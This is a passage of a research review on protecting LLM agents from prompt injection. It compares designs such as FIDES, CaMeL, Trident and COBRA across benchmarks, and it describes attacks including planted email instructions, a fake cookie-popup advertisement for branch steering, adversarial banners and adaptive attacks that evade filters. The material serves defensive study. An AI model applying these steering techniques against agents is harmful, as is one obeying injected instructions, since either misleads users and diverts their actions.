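- **TCR@k** is the percentage of all tasks that the agent completes with v ≤ k. TCR stands for "task completion rate", so TCR@0 counts only tasks completed without any questions.

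They compared Prudentia with FIDES and with a basic agent that asks before every consequential action. These are the averages on AgentDojo:

| Model | HITL load, basic | HITL load, FIDES | HITL load, Prudentia | TCR@0, basic | TCR@0, FIDES | TCR@0, Prudentia |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 59.4 | 7.8 | 23.8 | 28.0% | 50.3% | 42.5% |
| o3-mini | 48.2 | 18.8 | 16.4 | 24.3% | 50.1% | 59.1% |
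| o4-mini | 48.6 | 36.8 | 19.2 | 32.8% | 53.2% | 59.4% |
| GPT-5 | 52.0 | 41.3 | 7.3 | 35.1% | 57.1% | 72.7% |

With GPT-5, Prudentia asked roughly one question for every ten tasks it completed, while FIDES asked roughly one for every two. With no limit on questions, both agents completed about 80% of the tasks.

Prudentia did worse than FIDES on both HITL load and TCR@0 with GPT-4o, the oldest of the four models. FIDES's load was low partly because it failed some tasks, and HITL load counts only completed ones. That doesn't explain the gap in TCR@0, so Prudentia's extra planning probably needs a stronger model. The planning also made Prudentia use roughly two to six times as many input tokens as FIDES on the three models for which Kolluri and colleagues reported token use.

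Another test of Prudentia used WASP, a benchmark in which an agent uses simulated versions of GitLab and Reddit while attackers plant instructions in posts. The models were GPT-4o, o1, o3-mini and o4-mini. Attacks diverted the basic agent in 14.6% to 61.1% of cases, depending on the model and website, but never diverted Prudentia. The basic agent needed an average of 1.0 to 3.7 approvals per task, and Prudentia needed none.

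The WASP tasks were easy to secure because the user only wanted to comment on a post or upvote it, and Prudentia could do either without reading untrusted text. AgentDojo's tasks more often depend on what such text contains, so its results are a better guide to how often an agent would have to ask for human approval.

### Whether people judge well

No people took part in these tests. Kolluri and colleagues counted the questions each agent would have asked during tasks without attacks, and assumed that the user would approve every one in a successful run. They also assumed that a person would refuse any call caused by an injection. Prudentia's security on AgentDojo therefore depends partly on perfect human judgement. On WASP, Prudentia never had to ask for approval, so its result there doesn't depend on that judgement.

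People who see many approval requests may start approving them without reading, which Kolluri and colleagues call confirmation fatigue. They cite research by Stanton and colleagues (2016) on security fatigue, and by Seidling and colleagues (2011) on the alerts that users of medical software accept. Microsoft likewise warns that human approval "scales poorly" and "erodes vigilance". But neither Microsoft nor Kolluri and colleagues measured how often users approve an agent's malicious request, so it is unclear how much protection approval gives.

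One way to limit fatigue is to ask only when the stakes are high. Tallam and Miller propose three levels for CaMeL:

| Level | Example | Check |
|---|---|---|
| Green | listing calendar events | a basic check of where the data came from |
| Yellow | moving a file to a shared folder | a quick confirmation if any argument is untrusted |
| Red | sending an email or a bank transfer | all policy checks, plus approval with more than one proof of identity |

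They did not test these levels with CaMeL. The yellow example also shows that actions are hard to sort by risk, because moving a file to a shared folder may reveal it to many people.

An attacker who can influence the text of an approval request may make a harmful action look routine. Kolluri and colleagues suggest showing the data's labels and origin, which the attacker cannot change. For the email to Bob, a useful request would show that his address came from notes that outsiders can edit. Agent Framework's requests show the tool and the label that caused the block, though Microsoft acknowledges that they are still coarse.

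Kolluri and colleagues point out that even a perfect policy would not remove every reason to ask the user for approval, because a model can still misunderstand a request and, for example, choose the wrong person named Bob.

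## Tasks that become impossible or harder

A policy that stops untrusted text from determining an agent's actions affects some requests far more than others. If Alice asks her assistant to tell Jane that she'll be 15 minutes late, the assistant can plan every step from her request alone, so the policy doesn't interfere. But if she asks it to do whatever Jane's email says, the steps depend on the email, which the policy forbids. Costa and colleagues defined this difference formally and used the definition to sort the tasks in AgentDojo.

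### Data independence and realizability

Costa and colleagues describe a task t as a triple (q, T, D), where q is the user's request, T is the list of tools, and D is the set of states the stored data might be in, such as all the possible contents of Alice's mailbox. For each state d in D, ⟦t⟧(d) is the set of action sequences that solve the task in that state. An action is a tool call or the final reply, but not a query to the model.

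A task is data-independent if at least one sequence solves it in every state:

⋂ ⟦t⟧(d) ≠ ∅, where the intersection runs over all d in D

Otherwise it is data-dependent, and the agent has to learn something about the data before it can know what to do.

Copying text does not by itself make a task data-dependent. Emailing a file to Bob takes the same sequence of calls whatever the file contains, as long as the call refers to the contents by a variable name. If the sequence had to include the text itself, each different file would need a different sequence.

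The other definition concerns what a particular design can do. Costa and colleagues use "planner" for the software that decides what the model sees and what happens to its output. A planner P realizes a task under a model M if

for every d in D, Loop(σ₀, d, q) ∈ ⟦t⟧(d)

Loop(σ₀, d, q) is the sequence of actions the agent takes when P starts from its initial state σ₀. To meet the definition, the agent must succeed with every possible mailbox.

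An agent can fail a task because P withholds information that any model would need, or because M has the information and uses it badly. To tell these apart, Costa and colleagues sometimes ask only whether any model could complete the task, even an imaginary one that always makes the best choice. If that model would fail too, the design makes the task impossible.

### Three email tasks

Costa and colleagues work through three requests to an office assistant:

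1. **Forward:** send the top three emails in the mailbox to a colleague as a chat message.
2. **Summarise:** send the colleague a summary of those emails instead.
3. **Schedule:** check whether any of the emails asks for a meeting and, if so, create the calendar event.

Several designs are compared under one rule, which allows a tool call only if the model chose it based on trusted inputs. The rule applies only to the choice of call, so the arguments may still contain untrusted text.

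| Design | Forward | Summarise | Schedule |
|---|---|---|---|
| Basic loop, where the model reads everything | breaks the rule | breaks the rule | breaks the rule if there is a request |
| Variables that the model cannot open | works | cannot do it | cannot do it |
| Variables that the model can open | works | breaks the rule | breaks the rule |
| Variables and a quarantined model | works | works | cannot do it |
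| FIDES, with yes-or-no answers | works | works | works with an exception |

The planner can forward emails using only the name of the variable that holds them. Summarizing them requires a model to read the text, but the quarantined model can do that, and the planner can send the summary without seeing it. A hostile email could still make the summary false or empty.

Scheduling is different because the emails determine whether a second step is needed. The quarantined model can determine this, but its answer goes into another variable that the planner can't read, so the planner can't act on it. FIDES lets the planner read a yes-or-no answer, which lets untrusted data influence the planner by one bit and so requires the looser policy described earlier.

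CaMeL could handle the same request with an `if` statement in its program. The answer would never reach its planner, but an outsider's email would still determine whether the event appears in the calendar, so this is also an exception to the strict rule. This approach works only because the user's request already specifies the step that might follow.

### What a better model can fix

Under a strict rule, an agent cannot carry out a request to do whatever a file says. *Trident* (2026), which presents an agent design for data-dependent tasks, argues that no policy can always tell the user's intent from the attacker's in such a request. If Alice says "Do what Jane's email says", the agent has as much reason to follow a line an attacker planted in the email as it does to follow Jane's own sentences. A better model might guess more accurately which lines Jane wrote, but guessing from the text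 is a form of filtering, which attackers can adapt to.

Other tasks are possible only with an exception to the policy. The meeting request is one example, and paying a bill is another if the policy requires a trusted recipient and the account number appears only in the bill. Someone has to decide that the risk is acceptable, even with a better model, because the account number still comes from an untrusted source.

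The remaining failures come from the model's mistakes. Costa and colleagues found that GPT-4o confused variable names, made unnecessary calls and used the quarantined model inconsistently. In one chat task, the user had named the channel, but the planner listed all the channels, which brought in untrusted data for no benefit. A better model can avoid such mistakes.

Their results with two models, OpenAI's GPT-4o and its later reasoning model o1, make it possible to separate these costs. The table gives simple averages over AgentDojo's four sets of tasks, without attacks:

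| | GPT-4o | o1 |
|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, no policy checks | 84.3% | 84.0% |
| FIDES, no policy checks | 60.6% | 77.6% |
| FIDES, with policy checks | 50.0% | 60.8% |

With GPT-4o, having to work through variables lowered task completion by about 24 percentage points, and the policy lowered it by another 11. With o1, the variables lowered it by only about 6 points, but the policy lowered it by 17. The policy probably had a larger effect with o1 because o1 could get further with tasks that the policy then blocked.

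Some of the policy's burden is avoidable, because a planner can taint its own conversation unnecessarily. In tests by Kolluri and colleagues with o4-mini, Prudentia, whose planner knows the policies, completed 73.2% of tasks, slightly fewer than the 75.7% FIDES completed, but needed only about half as many human approvals.

### FIDES on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues sorted AgentDojo's 97 user tasks by hand:

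| AgentDojo tasks | Data-independent, no reading needed | Data-independent, with a quarantined model | Data-dependent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 47.5% | 47.5% | 5.0% |
| Travel | 0% | 90.0% | 10.0% |
| Banking | 18.7% | 37.5% | 43.8% |
| Chat | 19.0% | 38.1% | 42.9% |

About 20 of the 97 tasks are data-dependent, nearly all of them in banking and chat. Under the policies in this test, a perfect model should be able to complete every data-independent task, so their share is a rough ceiling for FIDES. The next table compares that ceiling with the tasks completed when policy checks were on and nobody was attacking:

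| AgentDojo tasks | Data-independent share | Basic, GPT-4o | FIDES, GPT-4o | Basic, o1 | FIDES, o1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 95.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% | 48.0% | 64.5% |
| Travel | 90.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% | 75.0% | 68.0% |
| Banking | 56.2% | 37.5% | 52.5% | 37.5% | 56.2% |
| Chat | 57.1% | 20.0% | 47.6% | 17.1% | 54.3% |

FIDES beat the basic agent by about 8 points on average with GPT-4o and 16 with o1. Costa and colleagues conclude that it approaches the performance of a human oracle. This holds for banking and chat tasks, where o1 nearly matched the oracle, but on office tasks it fell about 30 points short. Much of that shortfall is unrelated to security, since o1 completed only 70% of the office tasks even in the basic agent without security checks.

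Travel is the only area where the basic agent did better than FIDES under both models. The policies let many travel tools run after the agent has read untrusted text, so they did not reduce the basic agent's performance, while FIDES still had to work through variables.

The ceiling is only approximate, because agents completed some tasks that should have been impossible for them. Costa and colleagues also tested a simpler agent that could neither open its variables nor query a quarantined model. That design should rule out every travel task, but with GPT-4o the agent completed 44% of them. Part of the reason was that the planner guessed, for example by recommending the right hotel without seeing any ratings. The benchmark also checked some answers too loosely, and in a few tasks the correct response was to do nothing. With o1, the same agent completed only 4% of the travel tasks, so a higher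 score on this benchmark does not always mean a better agent.

The scores also depend on lenient policies. For tools that send money, change a password or book a hotel, FIDES ignored the labels on the arguments and checked only whether the planner's choice of call was trusted. A false account number in a bill would therefore have passed the check, like the swapped email address described earlier. A policy that also required a trusted recipient would probably have lowered the scores, because it would have blocked payment of genuine bills whose account number appears nowhere else.

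### Why the attack counts differ

Costa and colleagues also ran AgentDojo's attacks against each design with GPT-4o. The table gives the number of successful injections by the benchmark's own scoring. Where their manual inspection of the cases left a different number, it follows in brackets. "Tool Filter" is a defence in which the model starts by discarding the tools it won't need.

| Design | Office | Travel | Banking | Chat |
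|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, no checks | 33 | 19 (11) | 48 | 60 |
| Tool Filter | 4 | 5 (0) | 10 | 6 |
| Variables only, no checks | 0 | 12 (0) | 0 | 0 |
| FIDES, no checks | 1 | 2 (0) | 7 | 13 |
| Basic, with checks | 0 | 11 (0) | 0 | 7 (0) |
| Variables only, with checks | 0 | 14 (0) | 0 | 0 |
| FIDES, with checks | 0 | 0 | 0 | 3 (0) |

For the basic agent with checks, Costa and colleagues report a total of 20, but the four cells add up to 18. The corrected total is zero either way.

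The researchers discounted attacks that did only what the policies allow, such as creating a calendar event with no guests, and attacks that changed only the agent's words. They also corrected a scoring flaw in AgentDojo, which counts one chat attack, an attempt to invite an outsider to the workspace, as successful once the agent makes the call, even if the policy then blocks it.

A blocked call is clearly not a successful attack, but the other two corrections depend on what the policy is meant to prevent. An outsider who can add an event to Alice's calendar or recommend a hotel through her assistant has still influenced the agent. The zeros therefore mean only that no attack broke the policies. The basic agent with checks also scored zero, so FIDES's advantage is that it can complete more tasks at that level of security.

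### Randori and CaMeL on banking tasks

Randori, the agent that Garby and colleagues wrote in LLMbda, plans before it reads, as CaMeL does. In a practice phase, the planner tests and corrects its program on an invented bank account, where every file contains the same line of placeholder text. Nothing in the account comes from an outsider, so the errors that the planner sees can't carry an injection. When the planner writes the final version for the real account, it has instructions to drop any names or descriptions it picked up from the invented data.

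The practice phase finds ordinary programming mistakes but misses label errors, because the interpreter does not raise them during practice. The planner must also finalize its program before seeing any real data. A program can therefore work on the invented account and then stop on the real one, with no further chance to repair it.

Garby and colleagues compared Randori with CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks and ran each task three times. They tested CaMeL with its policies off and on. The figures are tasks completed, with 95% confidence intervals:

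| System | GPT-5.2, no attack | GPT-5.2, under attack | MiMo-v2.5, no attack | MiMo-v2.5, under attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | 75.0% ± 18.9 | 65.0% ± 6.7 | 64.6% ± 22.0 | 59.5% ± 6.2 |
| CaMeL, policies off | 66.7% ± 23.4 | 71.1% ± 7.7 | 70.8% ± 21.4 | 72.2% ± 7.4 |
| CaMeL, policies on | 37.5% ± 26.6 | 30.0% ± 8.1 | 37.5% ± 26.6 | 41.5% ± 7.9 |

Without attacks, turning on the policies roughly halved CaMeL's score, while Randori scored about as well as CaMeL without policies. But with only 16 tasks, the uncertainty intervals are so wide that even those for Randori and CaMeL with policies overlap. Under attack, their intervals are narrower and do not overlap, but they were calculated by treating 144 combinations of task and attack as separate samples, although all of them come from the same 16 tasks. Many of the CaMeL runs under attack also did not finish.

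The two systems also aren't equally strict. Garby and colleagues gave Randori a subset of CaMeL's policies and acknowledge that its rules are looser. Randori's planner can also endorse untrusted values, such as an account number in a file. Its higher score is therefore evidence that allowing exceptions lets more tasks succeed, but weaker evidence on whether LLMbda can enforce the same policy while losing fewer tasks.

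Most of the attacks did not test the policies, because in 97 of the 144 combinations the attack needed a tool that the plan for the user's task would never include. Planning before reading untrusted data should defeat those attacks. Across both models, only 5 of 622 completed attack runs succeeded against CaMeL without policies, and none succeeded with them. Against these fixed attacks, CaMeL's policies blocked a lot of useful work and improved security only slightly. An attacker who knew the design would target the values in the plan, where the policies matter more.

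In two of those five attacks, the user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. CaMeL's planner had to write its program before the file was read, so it included a branch for every tool and let the file's contents select which branches ran. This let the attacker choose almost any action without departing from the plan.

The Haskell agent system TypeGuard, like CaMeL, completes fewer tasks when its policies are on. Garby and colleagues cite results in which TypeGuard's score on AgentDojo's chat tasks fell from 15 of 21 to 8, compared with 7 for CaMeL under the same conditions. TypeGuard's developers observed that many of those tasks need data flows "that no secure policy would admit".

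### How far AgentDojo represents real work

AgentDojo's tasks are short and mostly predictable. In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) count only 6 of the 97 tasks as needing dynamic planning, in which the agent revises its plan as it learns more. The survey *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026) found the same weakness in all five benchmarks it reviewed, including AgentDojo.

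The count of 6 is much lower than the 20 data-dependent tasks in Costa and colleagues' classification, probably because the two groups used different criteria. Booking a hotel only if its rating is above 4 is data-dependent under the formal definition, but a planner can write both branches in advance. Working through a to-do list that the planner hasn't seen requires steps it could not have listed.

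AgentDojo also contains few harmless instructions from third parties, so a defence can score well by ignoring every instruction it finds. Real websites contain many useful ones, such as a request to log in before checking out.

Li and colleagues built AgentDyn to fill these gaps. It has 60 tasks in shopping, software projects and daily life. Every task needs dynamic planning and includes at least one helpful instruction that the agent has to follow.

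| Average per task | AgentDojo | AgentDyn |
|---|---|---|
| Tools available | 19.9 | 33.3 |
| Steps | 3.5 | 7.1 |
| Applications involved | 1.4 | 3.2 |

They tested ten defences, including CaMeL and two designs that adjust their restrictions during a run. Progent updates its policies as it goes. DRIFT makes a plan and then has a model judge whether any departure from it is justified. These are the results for two of the models:

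| Defence | Tasks completed, GPT-4o | Attacks successful, GPT-4o | Tasks completed, Gemini 2.5 Pro | Attacks successful, Gemini 2.5 Pro |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 37.8% | 51.7% | 20.6% |
| CaMeL | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 1.7% | 25.0% | 1.6% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 0.8% | 36.7% | 1.1% |

CaMeL also completed no tasks with the other two models in the main test, Claude 3.5 Sonnet and Llama 3.3 70B. A stronger planner would not help much, because the planner needs information that does not exist until the task is under way. CaMeL's perfect security score is uninformative, since an agent that completes no tasks may never reach the point where an attack could work.

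The best result with a defense came from Meta SecAlign, a model trained to ignore planted instructions. It completed 55% of the tasks, and 9% of the attacks on it succeeded. Those attacks used a fixed template, and in other tests the adaptive attacks by Nasr and colleagues succeeded against the same model 96% of the time.

AgentDyn is a deliberately harsh test of planning ahead, because Li and colleagues included only tasks that need dynamic planning. CaMeL scored zero on these tasks, but the benchmark doesn't measure how common they are. Li and colleagues also instructed every agent not to ask the user for confirmation, which removed the usual way to make an exception. They did not test the FIDES defence.

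WebArena, a benchmark of tasks on simulated websites, gives the opposite impression. Chow, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*, cite an analysis that sorted its tasks by what a program written in advance would need:

- Ordinary code can do 81% of the tasks, such as adding the highest-rated headphones under $200 to a shopping cart.
- Another 19% also need a model to interpret text, for example to summarise reviews, but the steps stay fixed.
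- None of the tasks takes its steps from untrusted content.

Chow and colleagues' own system, Baya, writes its whole program before visiting the live site. It completed 77.8% of the tasks in a corrected version of WebArena, compared with 66.7% for an ordinary agent that could also use the sites' programming interfaces, so planning ahead can improve an agent's performance when the task suits it. But the researchers had to describe each website's functions by hand in advance, and they acknowledge that Baya cannot support a request to do whatever the boss's email says.

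The share of tasks that need new steps from untrusted data is zero in WebArena, about 6% in AgentDojo and 100% in AgentDyn. These figures reflect what the benchmarks' designers chose to include, and none of the three is a sample of the requests people give their agents. A company could estimate how many tasks CaMeL or FIDES would block or make harder by checking how many of a few hundred of its own users' requests need such steps.

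### Open requests are also the easiest to attack

Attacks work best on the tasks that a strict rule excludes. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) sorts user tasks into three groups. In a fully specified task, the user gives the action and all its details. In a parameter-open task, the user names the action but leaves some details to the data, as when the user writes "Pay the bill" and gives a file name. In an action-open task, the data determines the action itself, as with a to-do list on a web page.

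With no defence, AgentDojo's standard attack succeeded against GPT-4o-mini in 87.5% of action-open cases and no more than 63.9% in either of the other groups. Ma and colleagues then had another model improve the attacks over six rounds, told only whether each attempt had worked. PIGuard, a filter that had stopped every standard attack on the same model, let through 17.3% of the improved attacks on fully specified tasks and 54.2% of those on action-open tasks. When the user has asked the agent to carry out whatever it finds, an attacker can write the injection as one more task, which gives a filter that looks for suspicious instructions little to detect.

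The improved attacks had less effect on systems that limit what the agent can do. Progent, DRIFT and ROPE, which checks whether sensitive arguments came from the user, kept the attack success rate at or below 11% in every group. This is partly because Progent and DRIFT often allow only read-only tools when the user hasn't named an action, which makes an attack harmless but also prevents the agent from completing the list. CaMeL was the most effective defence overall, but it lost the most useful work on four of the five models.

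### Requests that leave only part of the plan open

Many requests fall between a fully specified task and "do what this email says". In the main example in *Trident*, the user's manager, Jane, has forwarded a caterer's email about a team event. The user asks the agent to carry out the requests in the email, pay from the team account and let Jane know. The user specifies the sender, the subject and the payment account, but the actions depend on the email's contents.

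Trident's planner never reads the email. A second model reads it and can return only answers from a fixed range, such as yes or no to whether the email contains an invoice. A third model writes the policy from the user's request before any model reads the email. Ordinary software checks the output of all three.

The policy doesn't name the payee, but it allows only one payment, of at most $5,000, to an account on the company's own vendor list. New bank details in a planted line have no effect, because the software takes the account number from that list. A planted request to email the guests' dietary needs to an outside address also fails, because the policy allows email only to Jane and to a vendor contact already on file.

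The attacker can still use the email to choose which of the three listed vendors receives the money. The attacker can also set the amount, up to the limit, because there is no trusted record of what the company owes. The user could have lowered that limit by writing "at most $2,500".

Trident also limits how much the planner can learn from untrusted data during a task. Each answer uses up part of a budget β, measured in bits, and each piece of feedback that an attacker could cause, such as a failed query, uses up part of a second budget σ. With the trusted inputs and the models' randomness held fixed, an attacker can choose among at most

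2^(β+σ)

different sequences of visible actions. With a combined budget of ten bits, that makes 1,024. *Trident* proves this limit in Lean, and also proves that every call the agent makes satisfies a general policy written by an administrator. The proofs do not depend on any of the models behaving well. As with the sorted emails described earlier, a small number of possibilities can still include a harmful one, so the administrator's policy has to exclude it.

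The accompanying benchmark, ReplanInject, has 45 tasks that leave none, part or all of the plan to the data. Trident completed between 54% and 74% of them under attack, depending on the model, and on average it completed more than CaMeL, Progent and FIDES did. None of the attacks succeeded when a person could approve calls. The same team designed the system and the benchmark, so other open-ended tasks may suit Trident less well. For requests that leave everything to the data, *Trident* aims only to prevent the attack, even if the agent can't finish the task.

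## Agents that operate a screen

In the designs described so far, agents act through tools such as `send_email`, which a policy can refer to by name. But developers build most software for people, and much of it offers agents no such tools. To use it, an agent looks at a screenshot, chooses an action such as a click or a few keystrokes, then repeats this with a new screenshot.

Agents have become very good at operating a screen. OSWorld is a benchmark of 369 tasks on a real desktop, such as editing a spreadsheet or changing a browser setting. When it came out in 2024, the best model completed 12.2% of the tasks and people completed 72.4%. Huawei's openJiuwen team has since reached 93.5% on a revised version, OSWorld-Verified (*Towards Hyper Agents for Long-Horizon Computer Use*, 2026). According to Artificial Analysis' *Browser-based office work for AI agents is solved* (2026), the best models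 score 98% on 52 office tasks using only screenshots, clicks and keystrokes.

Operating a screen conflicts with keeping the planner away from untrusted data, because the model that chooses each click has to see the screen, which may show a stranger's message or an advertisement. In the basic labelled loop, one such screenshot would taint every later action.

### Why a policy cannot check a click

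A policy can restrict who receives an email, but it can do little with an action like `click(246, 1023)`. Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) point out in *ceLLMate* that the click's effect depends on the website, its current state and the screen's resolution, so the same click could open an email or delete it.

Restricting other low-level actions doesn't work well either. When Meng and colleagues blocked an agent from navigating directly to the website Hacker News, it could still get there by searching for the site and clicking the result.

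Researchers call this mismatch the semantic gap. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) contrasts agents with ordinary computers, which have several layers where a policy can apply. For example, the operating system controls which files a browser may write to, and the browser controls which cookies it sends to each website. An agent turns a broad request into low-level actions without such layers in between.

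### CaMeL-NOVA: one plan with many branches

In January 2026, Foerster and colleagues adapted CaMeL to screens. In their system, CaMeL-NOVA, the planner writes the whole program before any model looks at the screen. Part of a program might look like this, in simplified form:

```
summary = summarize_screenshot("What is on the screen?")
popup = verify_hypothesis(summary, "A cookie popup is visible")
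if popup == "OK":
    button = find("the button that accepts cookies")
    click(button)
```

1. **Observe.** A quarantined vision model describes the screen. The program can also read the page's underlying structure, which lists its buttons, links and text.
2. **Verify.** Another quarantined call checks whether the description matches a condition that the planner wrote in advance. It answers yes or no, or "unknown" if it cannot tell.
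3. **Act.** The interpreter uses the answer to select a branch. If the branch contains a click, the vision model finds the coordinates and the interpreter clicks there.

As in CaMeL, the planner never sees these results, so its plan has to cover every screen the agent might encounter. For the request "Browse the natural products database", the planner wrote separate branches for a website, an empty browser tab and the desktop, because the computer could be showing any of them. It also wrote several descriptions of the cookie button to try in turn.

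These programs are much longer than CaMeL's programs for AgentDojo:

| Average per plan | AgentDojo | OSWorld, basic CaMeL | OSWorld, CaMeL-NOVA |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 52 | 72 | 213 |
| Tool calls | 4.9 | 19.8 | 41.1 |
| Branches | 3.7 | 11.3 | 39.7 |

About half of the steps in a CaMeL-NOVA plan are fallbacks that do not run, but including them helps it complete many more tasks. On 60 OSWorld tasks, CaMeL-NOVA completed 35 within three attempts, compared with 11 for the basic version.

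In AgentDojo plans, 79% of branch conditions use only values from within the program, such as a loop counter, whereas about 91% of those in CaMeL-NOVA plans depend on what the agent finds on the screen or on whether an earlier action worked. An attacker who controls part of the screen therefore has many more decisions to influence in CaMeL-NOVA plans.

Foerster and colleagues also adapted FIDES, which plans one step at a time. They had to let its planner read the yes-or-no answers. To keep the planner from reconstructing the screen from many answers, they limited how often it could query the same variable. This version completed about as many tasks as CaMeL-NOVA within five attempts, but it used 29.6 times as many tokens as an unprotected agent, compared with 1.9 times for CaMeL-NOVA, because it sent the planner the full history at every step.

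### How much performance CaMeL-NOVA keeps

Foerster and colleagues report that CaMeL-NOVA keeps up to 57% of the performance of frontier models. That figure comes from a test with Claude Sonnet 4.5. Working alone, with one attempt and at most 15 steps per task, Sonnet completed 109 of the 339 OSWorld tasks that have automatic scoring. CaMeL-NOVA, with Sonnet as its vision model, then tried those 109 tasks:

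| Attempts allowed | Tasks completed at least once |
|---|---|
| 1 | 28% |
| 3 | 52% |
| 5 | 57% |

The 57% figure therefore compares five attempts with Sonnet's one. Achieving it in practice would also require a way to identify the successful attempt. On a real computer, a failed attempt might already have sent an email or changed a file. The 28% figure is more relevant for a user who needs the task done the first time.

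A reported gain for small models also depends on the number of attempts. UI-TARS, an open vision model with 7 billion parameters, scored 24.4% alone with one attempt. CaMeL-NOVA, using UI-TARS as its vision model, scored 29.0% with three attempts. On the first attempt, CaMeL-NOVA completed 51 of the 339 tasks, while UI-TARS alone completed 60.

The planner's foresight seems to be the main limit. CaMeL-NOVA completed 65% to 68% of one set of 60 tasks within five attempts with each of three very different vision models. When Foerster and colleagues varied the planner instead, the number of tasks completed ranged from 4 to 12 out of 17. Better planners should therefore help, but they still cannot complete data-dependent tasks whose steps appear only on the screen.

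Longer tasks may also be a problem. According to *Desktop-Delta Bench* (2026), agents make about 318 tool calls per task in OSWorld 2.0, a newer benchmark of professional work. A plan for such a task would need far more calls than the 41 in an average CaMeL-NOVA plan, and fallbacks for many more possible screens.

### Branch steering

In branch steering, an attacker uses a false appearance to lead the agent down a branch already in the plan. Control-flow integrity holds because the agent takes only planned steps in a planned order, but the harm comes from what those steps act on.

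Foerster and colleagues demonstrated this with an advertisement that looks like a cookie popup. The plan tells the agent to accept cookies if a popup appears. The vision model detects a popup and returns the coordinates of its button. The agent clicks there, which opens the attacker's website. The advertisement doesn't need to contain any instruction to the agent.

How much harm this can do depends on the user's task. To send the agent to a malicious site or make the task fail, an attacker may need to fake only one routine element. To steal money, the attacker needs a plan that already includes a payment and must mislead the vision model at least twice, for example about the recipient field and the confirm button. Leaking data requires a plan that both reads and sends data. CaMeL-NOVA therefore still rules out many attacks that would work on an ordinary screen agent.

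Foerster and colleagues tried to detect the false appearances with redundancy checks, in which another model reviews the vision model's answer. One check compares the answer with the page's underlying structure, and the other compares it with the screenshot:

| Check | Type of fake popup | Attacks flagged | Harmless tasks wrongly flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| Page structure | inside an ordinary image advertisement | 6 of 10 | 4 of 17 |
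| Screenshot | inside an advertisement with its own code | 5 of 10 | 3 of 17 |

Nearly all the false alarms were genuine cookie popups flagged as fake. The structure check works on image advertisements because the page marks them as advertising, but an attacker who can supply code for the advertisement can use it to replace that mark.

In a subtler attack, Foerster and colleagues altered the pixels of a banner so that it looked like random noise but changed how UI-TARS read the rest of the page. When asked to find the natural products database, UI-TARS chose a link to a particular drug and explained that the drug was a natural product. Neither check flagged this, because the link was genuine and the explanation sounded reasonable.

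Vision models also make such mistakes when nobody is attacking. In Artificial Analysis's office tests, misreading the screen caused 48% to 100% of the points lost by each of the seven models it examined.

### Checking the request behind the click

A click on a website usually matters because it makes the browser send a request to the site's server. Unlike the click, this request has a fixed meaning. On the code-hosting service GitLab, for example, a certain request always adds a key that gives its holder access to the user's account.

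Meng and colleagues built ceLLMate, a browser extension that checks these requests. It relies on an agent sitemap, which lists a website's security-relevant requests and describes what each one does. A policy can then allow an agent to place an order on Amazon only if the total is at most $50. The policy should also limit the number of orders, because otherwise the agent could place two orders of $49.

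Meng and colleagues simulated a completely hijacked agent with scripts that attempted 12 attacks on GitLab, such as deleting a project. The extension blocked all 12. But it applies the same permissions throughout a task, and it cannot stop an agent from misusing a permitted action, for example by posting a harmful comment.

### COBRA: different limits for each branch

COBRA, which Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, published in October 2026, combines CaMeL-NOVA's branching plans with checks on requests:

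1. The planner writes a program from the user's request and from descriptions of websites and tools that the user has approved. If an important value is missing, such as a delivery address, it asks the user.
2. The planner model then marks each branch with the websites, operations and argument values that the agent may use there.
3. The interpreter runs the program, and a quarantined vision model reads the screen.
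4. Ordinary code checks every web request and MCP tool call against the limits of the current branch. When the program leaves the branch, those permissions end.

If an advertisement were disguised as a cookie popup, the agent might still click it, but COBRA would block the request to the attacker's website because the plan does not list that site.

Zingrillo and colleagues tested COBRA on STEER-Bench, their own benchmark of 101 tasks such as bank transfers and changes to a patient's medication. None of the 199 attack cases succeeded. When they switched off the protection that each attack targeted, 174 succeeded, so most of the attacks were real threats. In the 74 cases that CaMeL-NOVA and an ordinary agent could run, attacks succeeded against them 87.8% and 90.5% of the time, respectively. Planning in advance, as CaMeL-NOVA does, therefore gave almost no protection against these attacks.

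COBRA kept 97% of CaMeL-NOVA's performance on harmless tasks and wrongly blocked legitimate actions in 4 of 138 runs. But its security depends on a model writing the right limits. Zingrillo and colleagues compared the model's limits for 30 cases with their own and found 28 correct. Of the other two, one was too strict and one would have allowed an unauthorised operation.

COBRA also blocked 1,289 of 1,312 attacks from four existing benchmarks. However, 1,223 of those attacks came from a benchmark of malicious tool descriptions, which makes the result weaker evidence about agents that operate a screen.

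### How much of the gap COBRA closes

To measure the cost in completed tasks, Zingrillo and colleagues used 361 tasks from OSWorld-MCP, a version of OSWorld in which agents can also call tools. Every agent had up to five attempts:

| Model that reads the screen | Ordinary agent | COBRA | COBRA's planner |
|---|---|---|---|
| UI-TARS | 23.5% | 36.8% | GPT-5 |
| OpenCUA-32B | 30.7% | 33.2% | GPT-5 |
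| Kimi K2.5 | 42.1% | 25.5% | Kimi K2.5 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 51.0% | 38.8% | Claude Sonnet 5 |

The gains for the two smaller models come at least partly from adding GPT-5, so the last two rows better show how much the restrictions reduce performance. COBRA kept about 76% of Sonnet 5's performance and 61% of Kimi's. This is a stronger result than CaMeL-NOVA's 57%, because both sides of the comparison had five attempts.

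On 86 shared tasks, COBRA completed 36 and CaMeL-NOVA 22. But the CaMeL-NOVA figure matches the results Foerster and colleagues reported for three attempts, while COBRA had five attempts and could also call tools. Better limits on each branch probably don't explain the difference, since limits can only block actions.

COBRA can also reduce the need for repeated attempts by generating five plans and merging them into one. With GPT-5 and UI-TARS, this raised the number of the 361 tasks completed on the first attempt from 78 to 105. This method cost about $0.59 per task, compared with $0.33 for the standard method.

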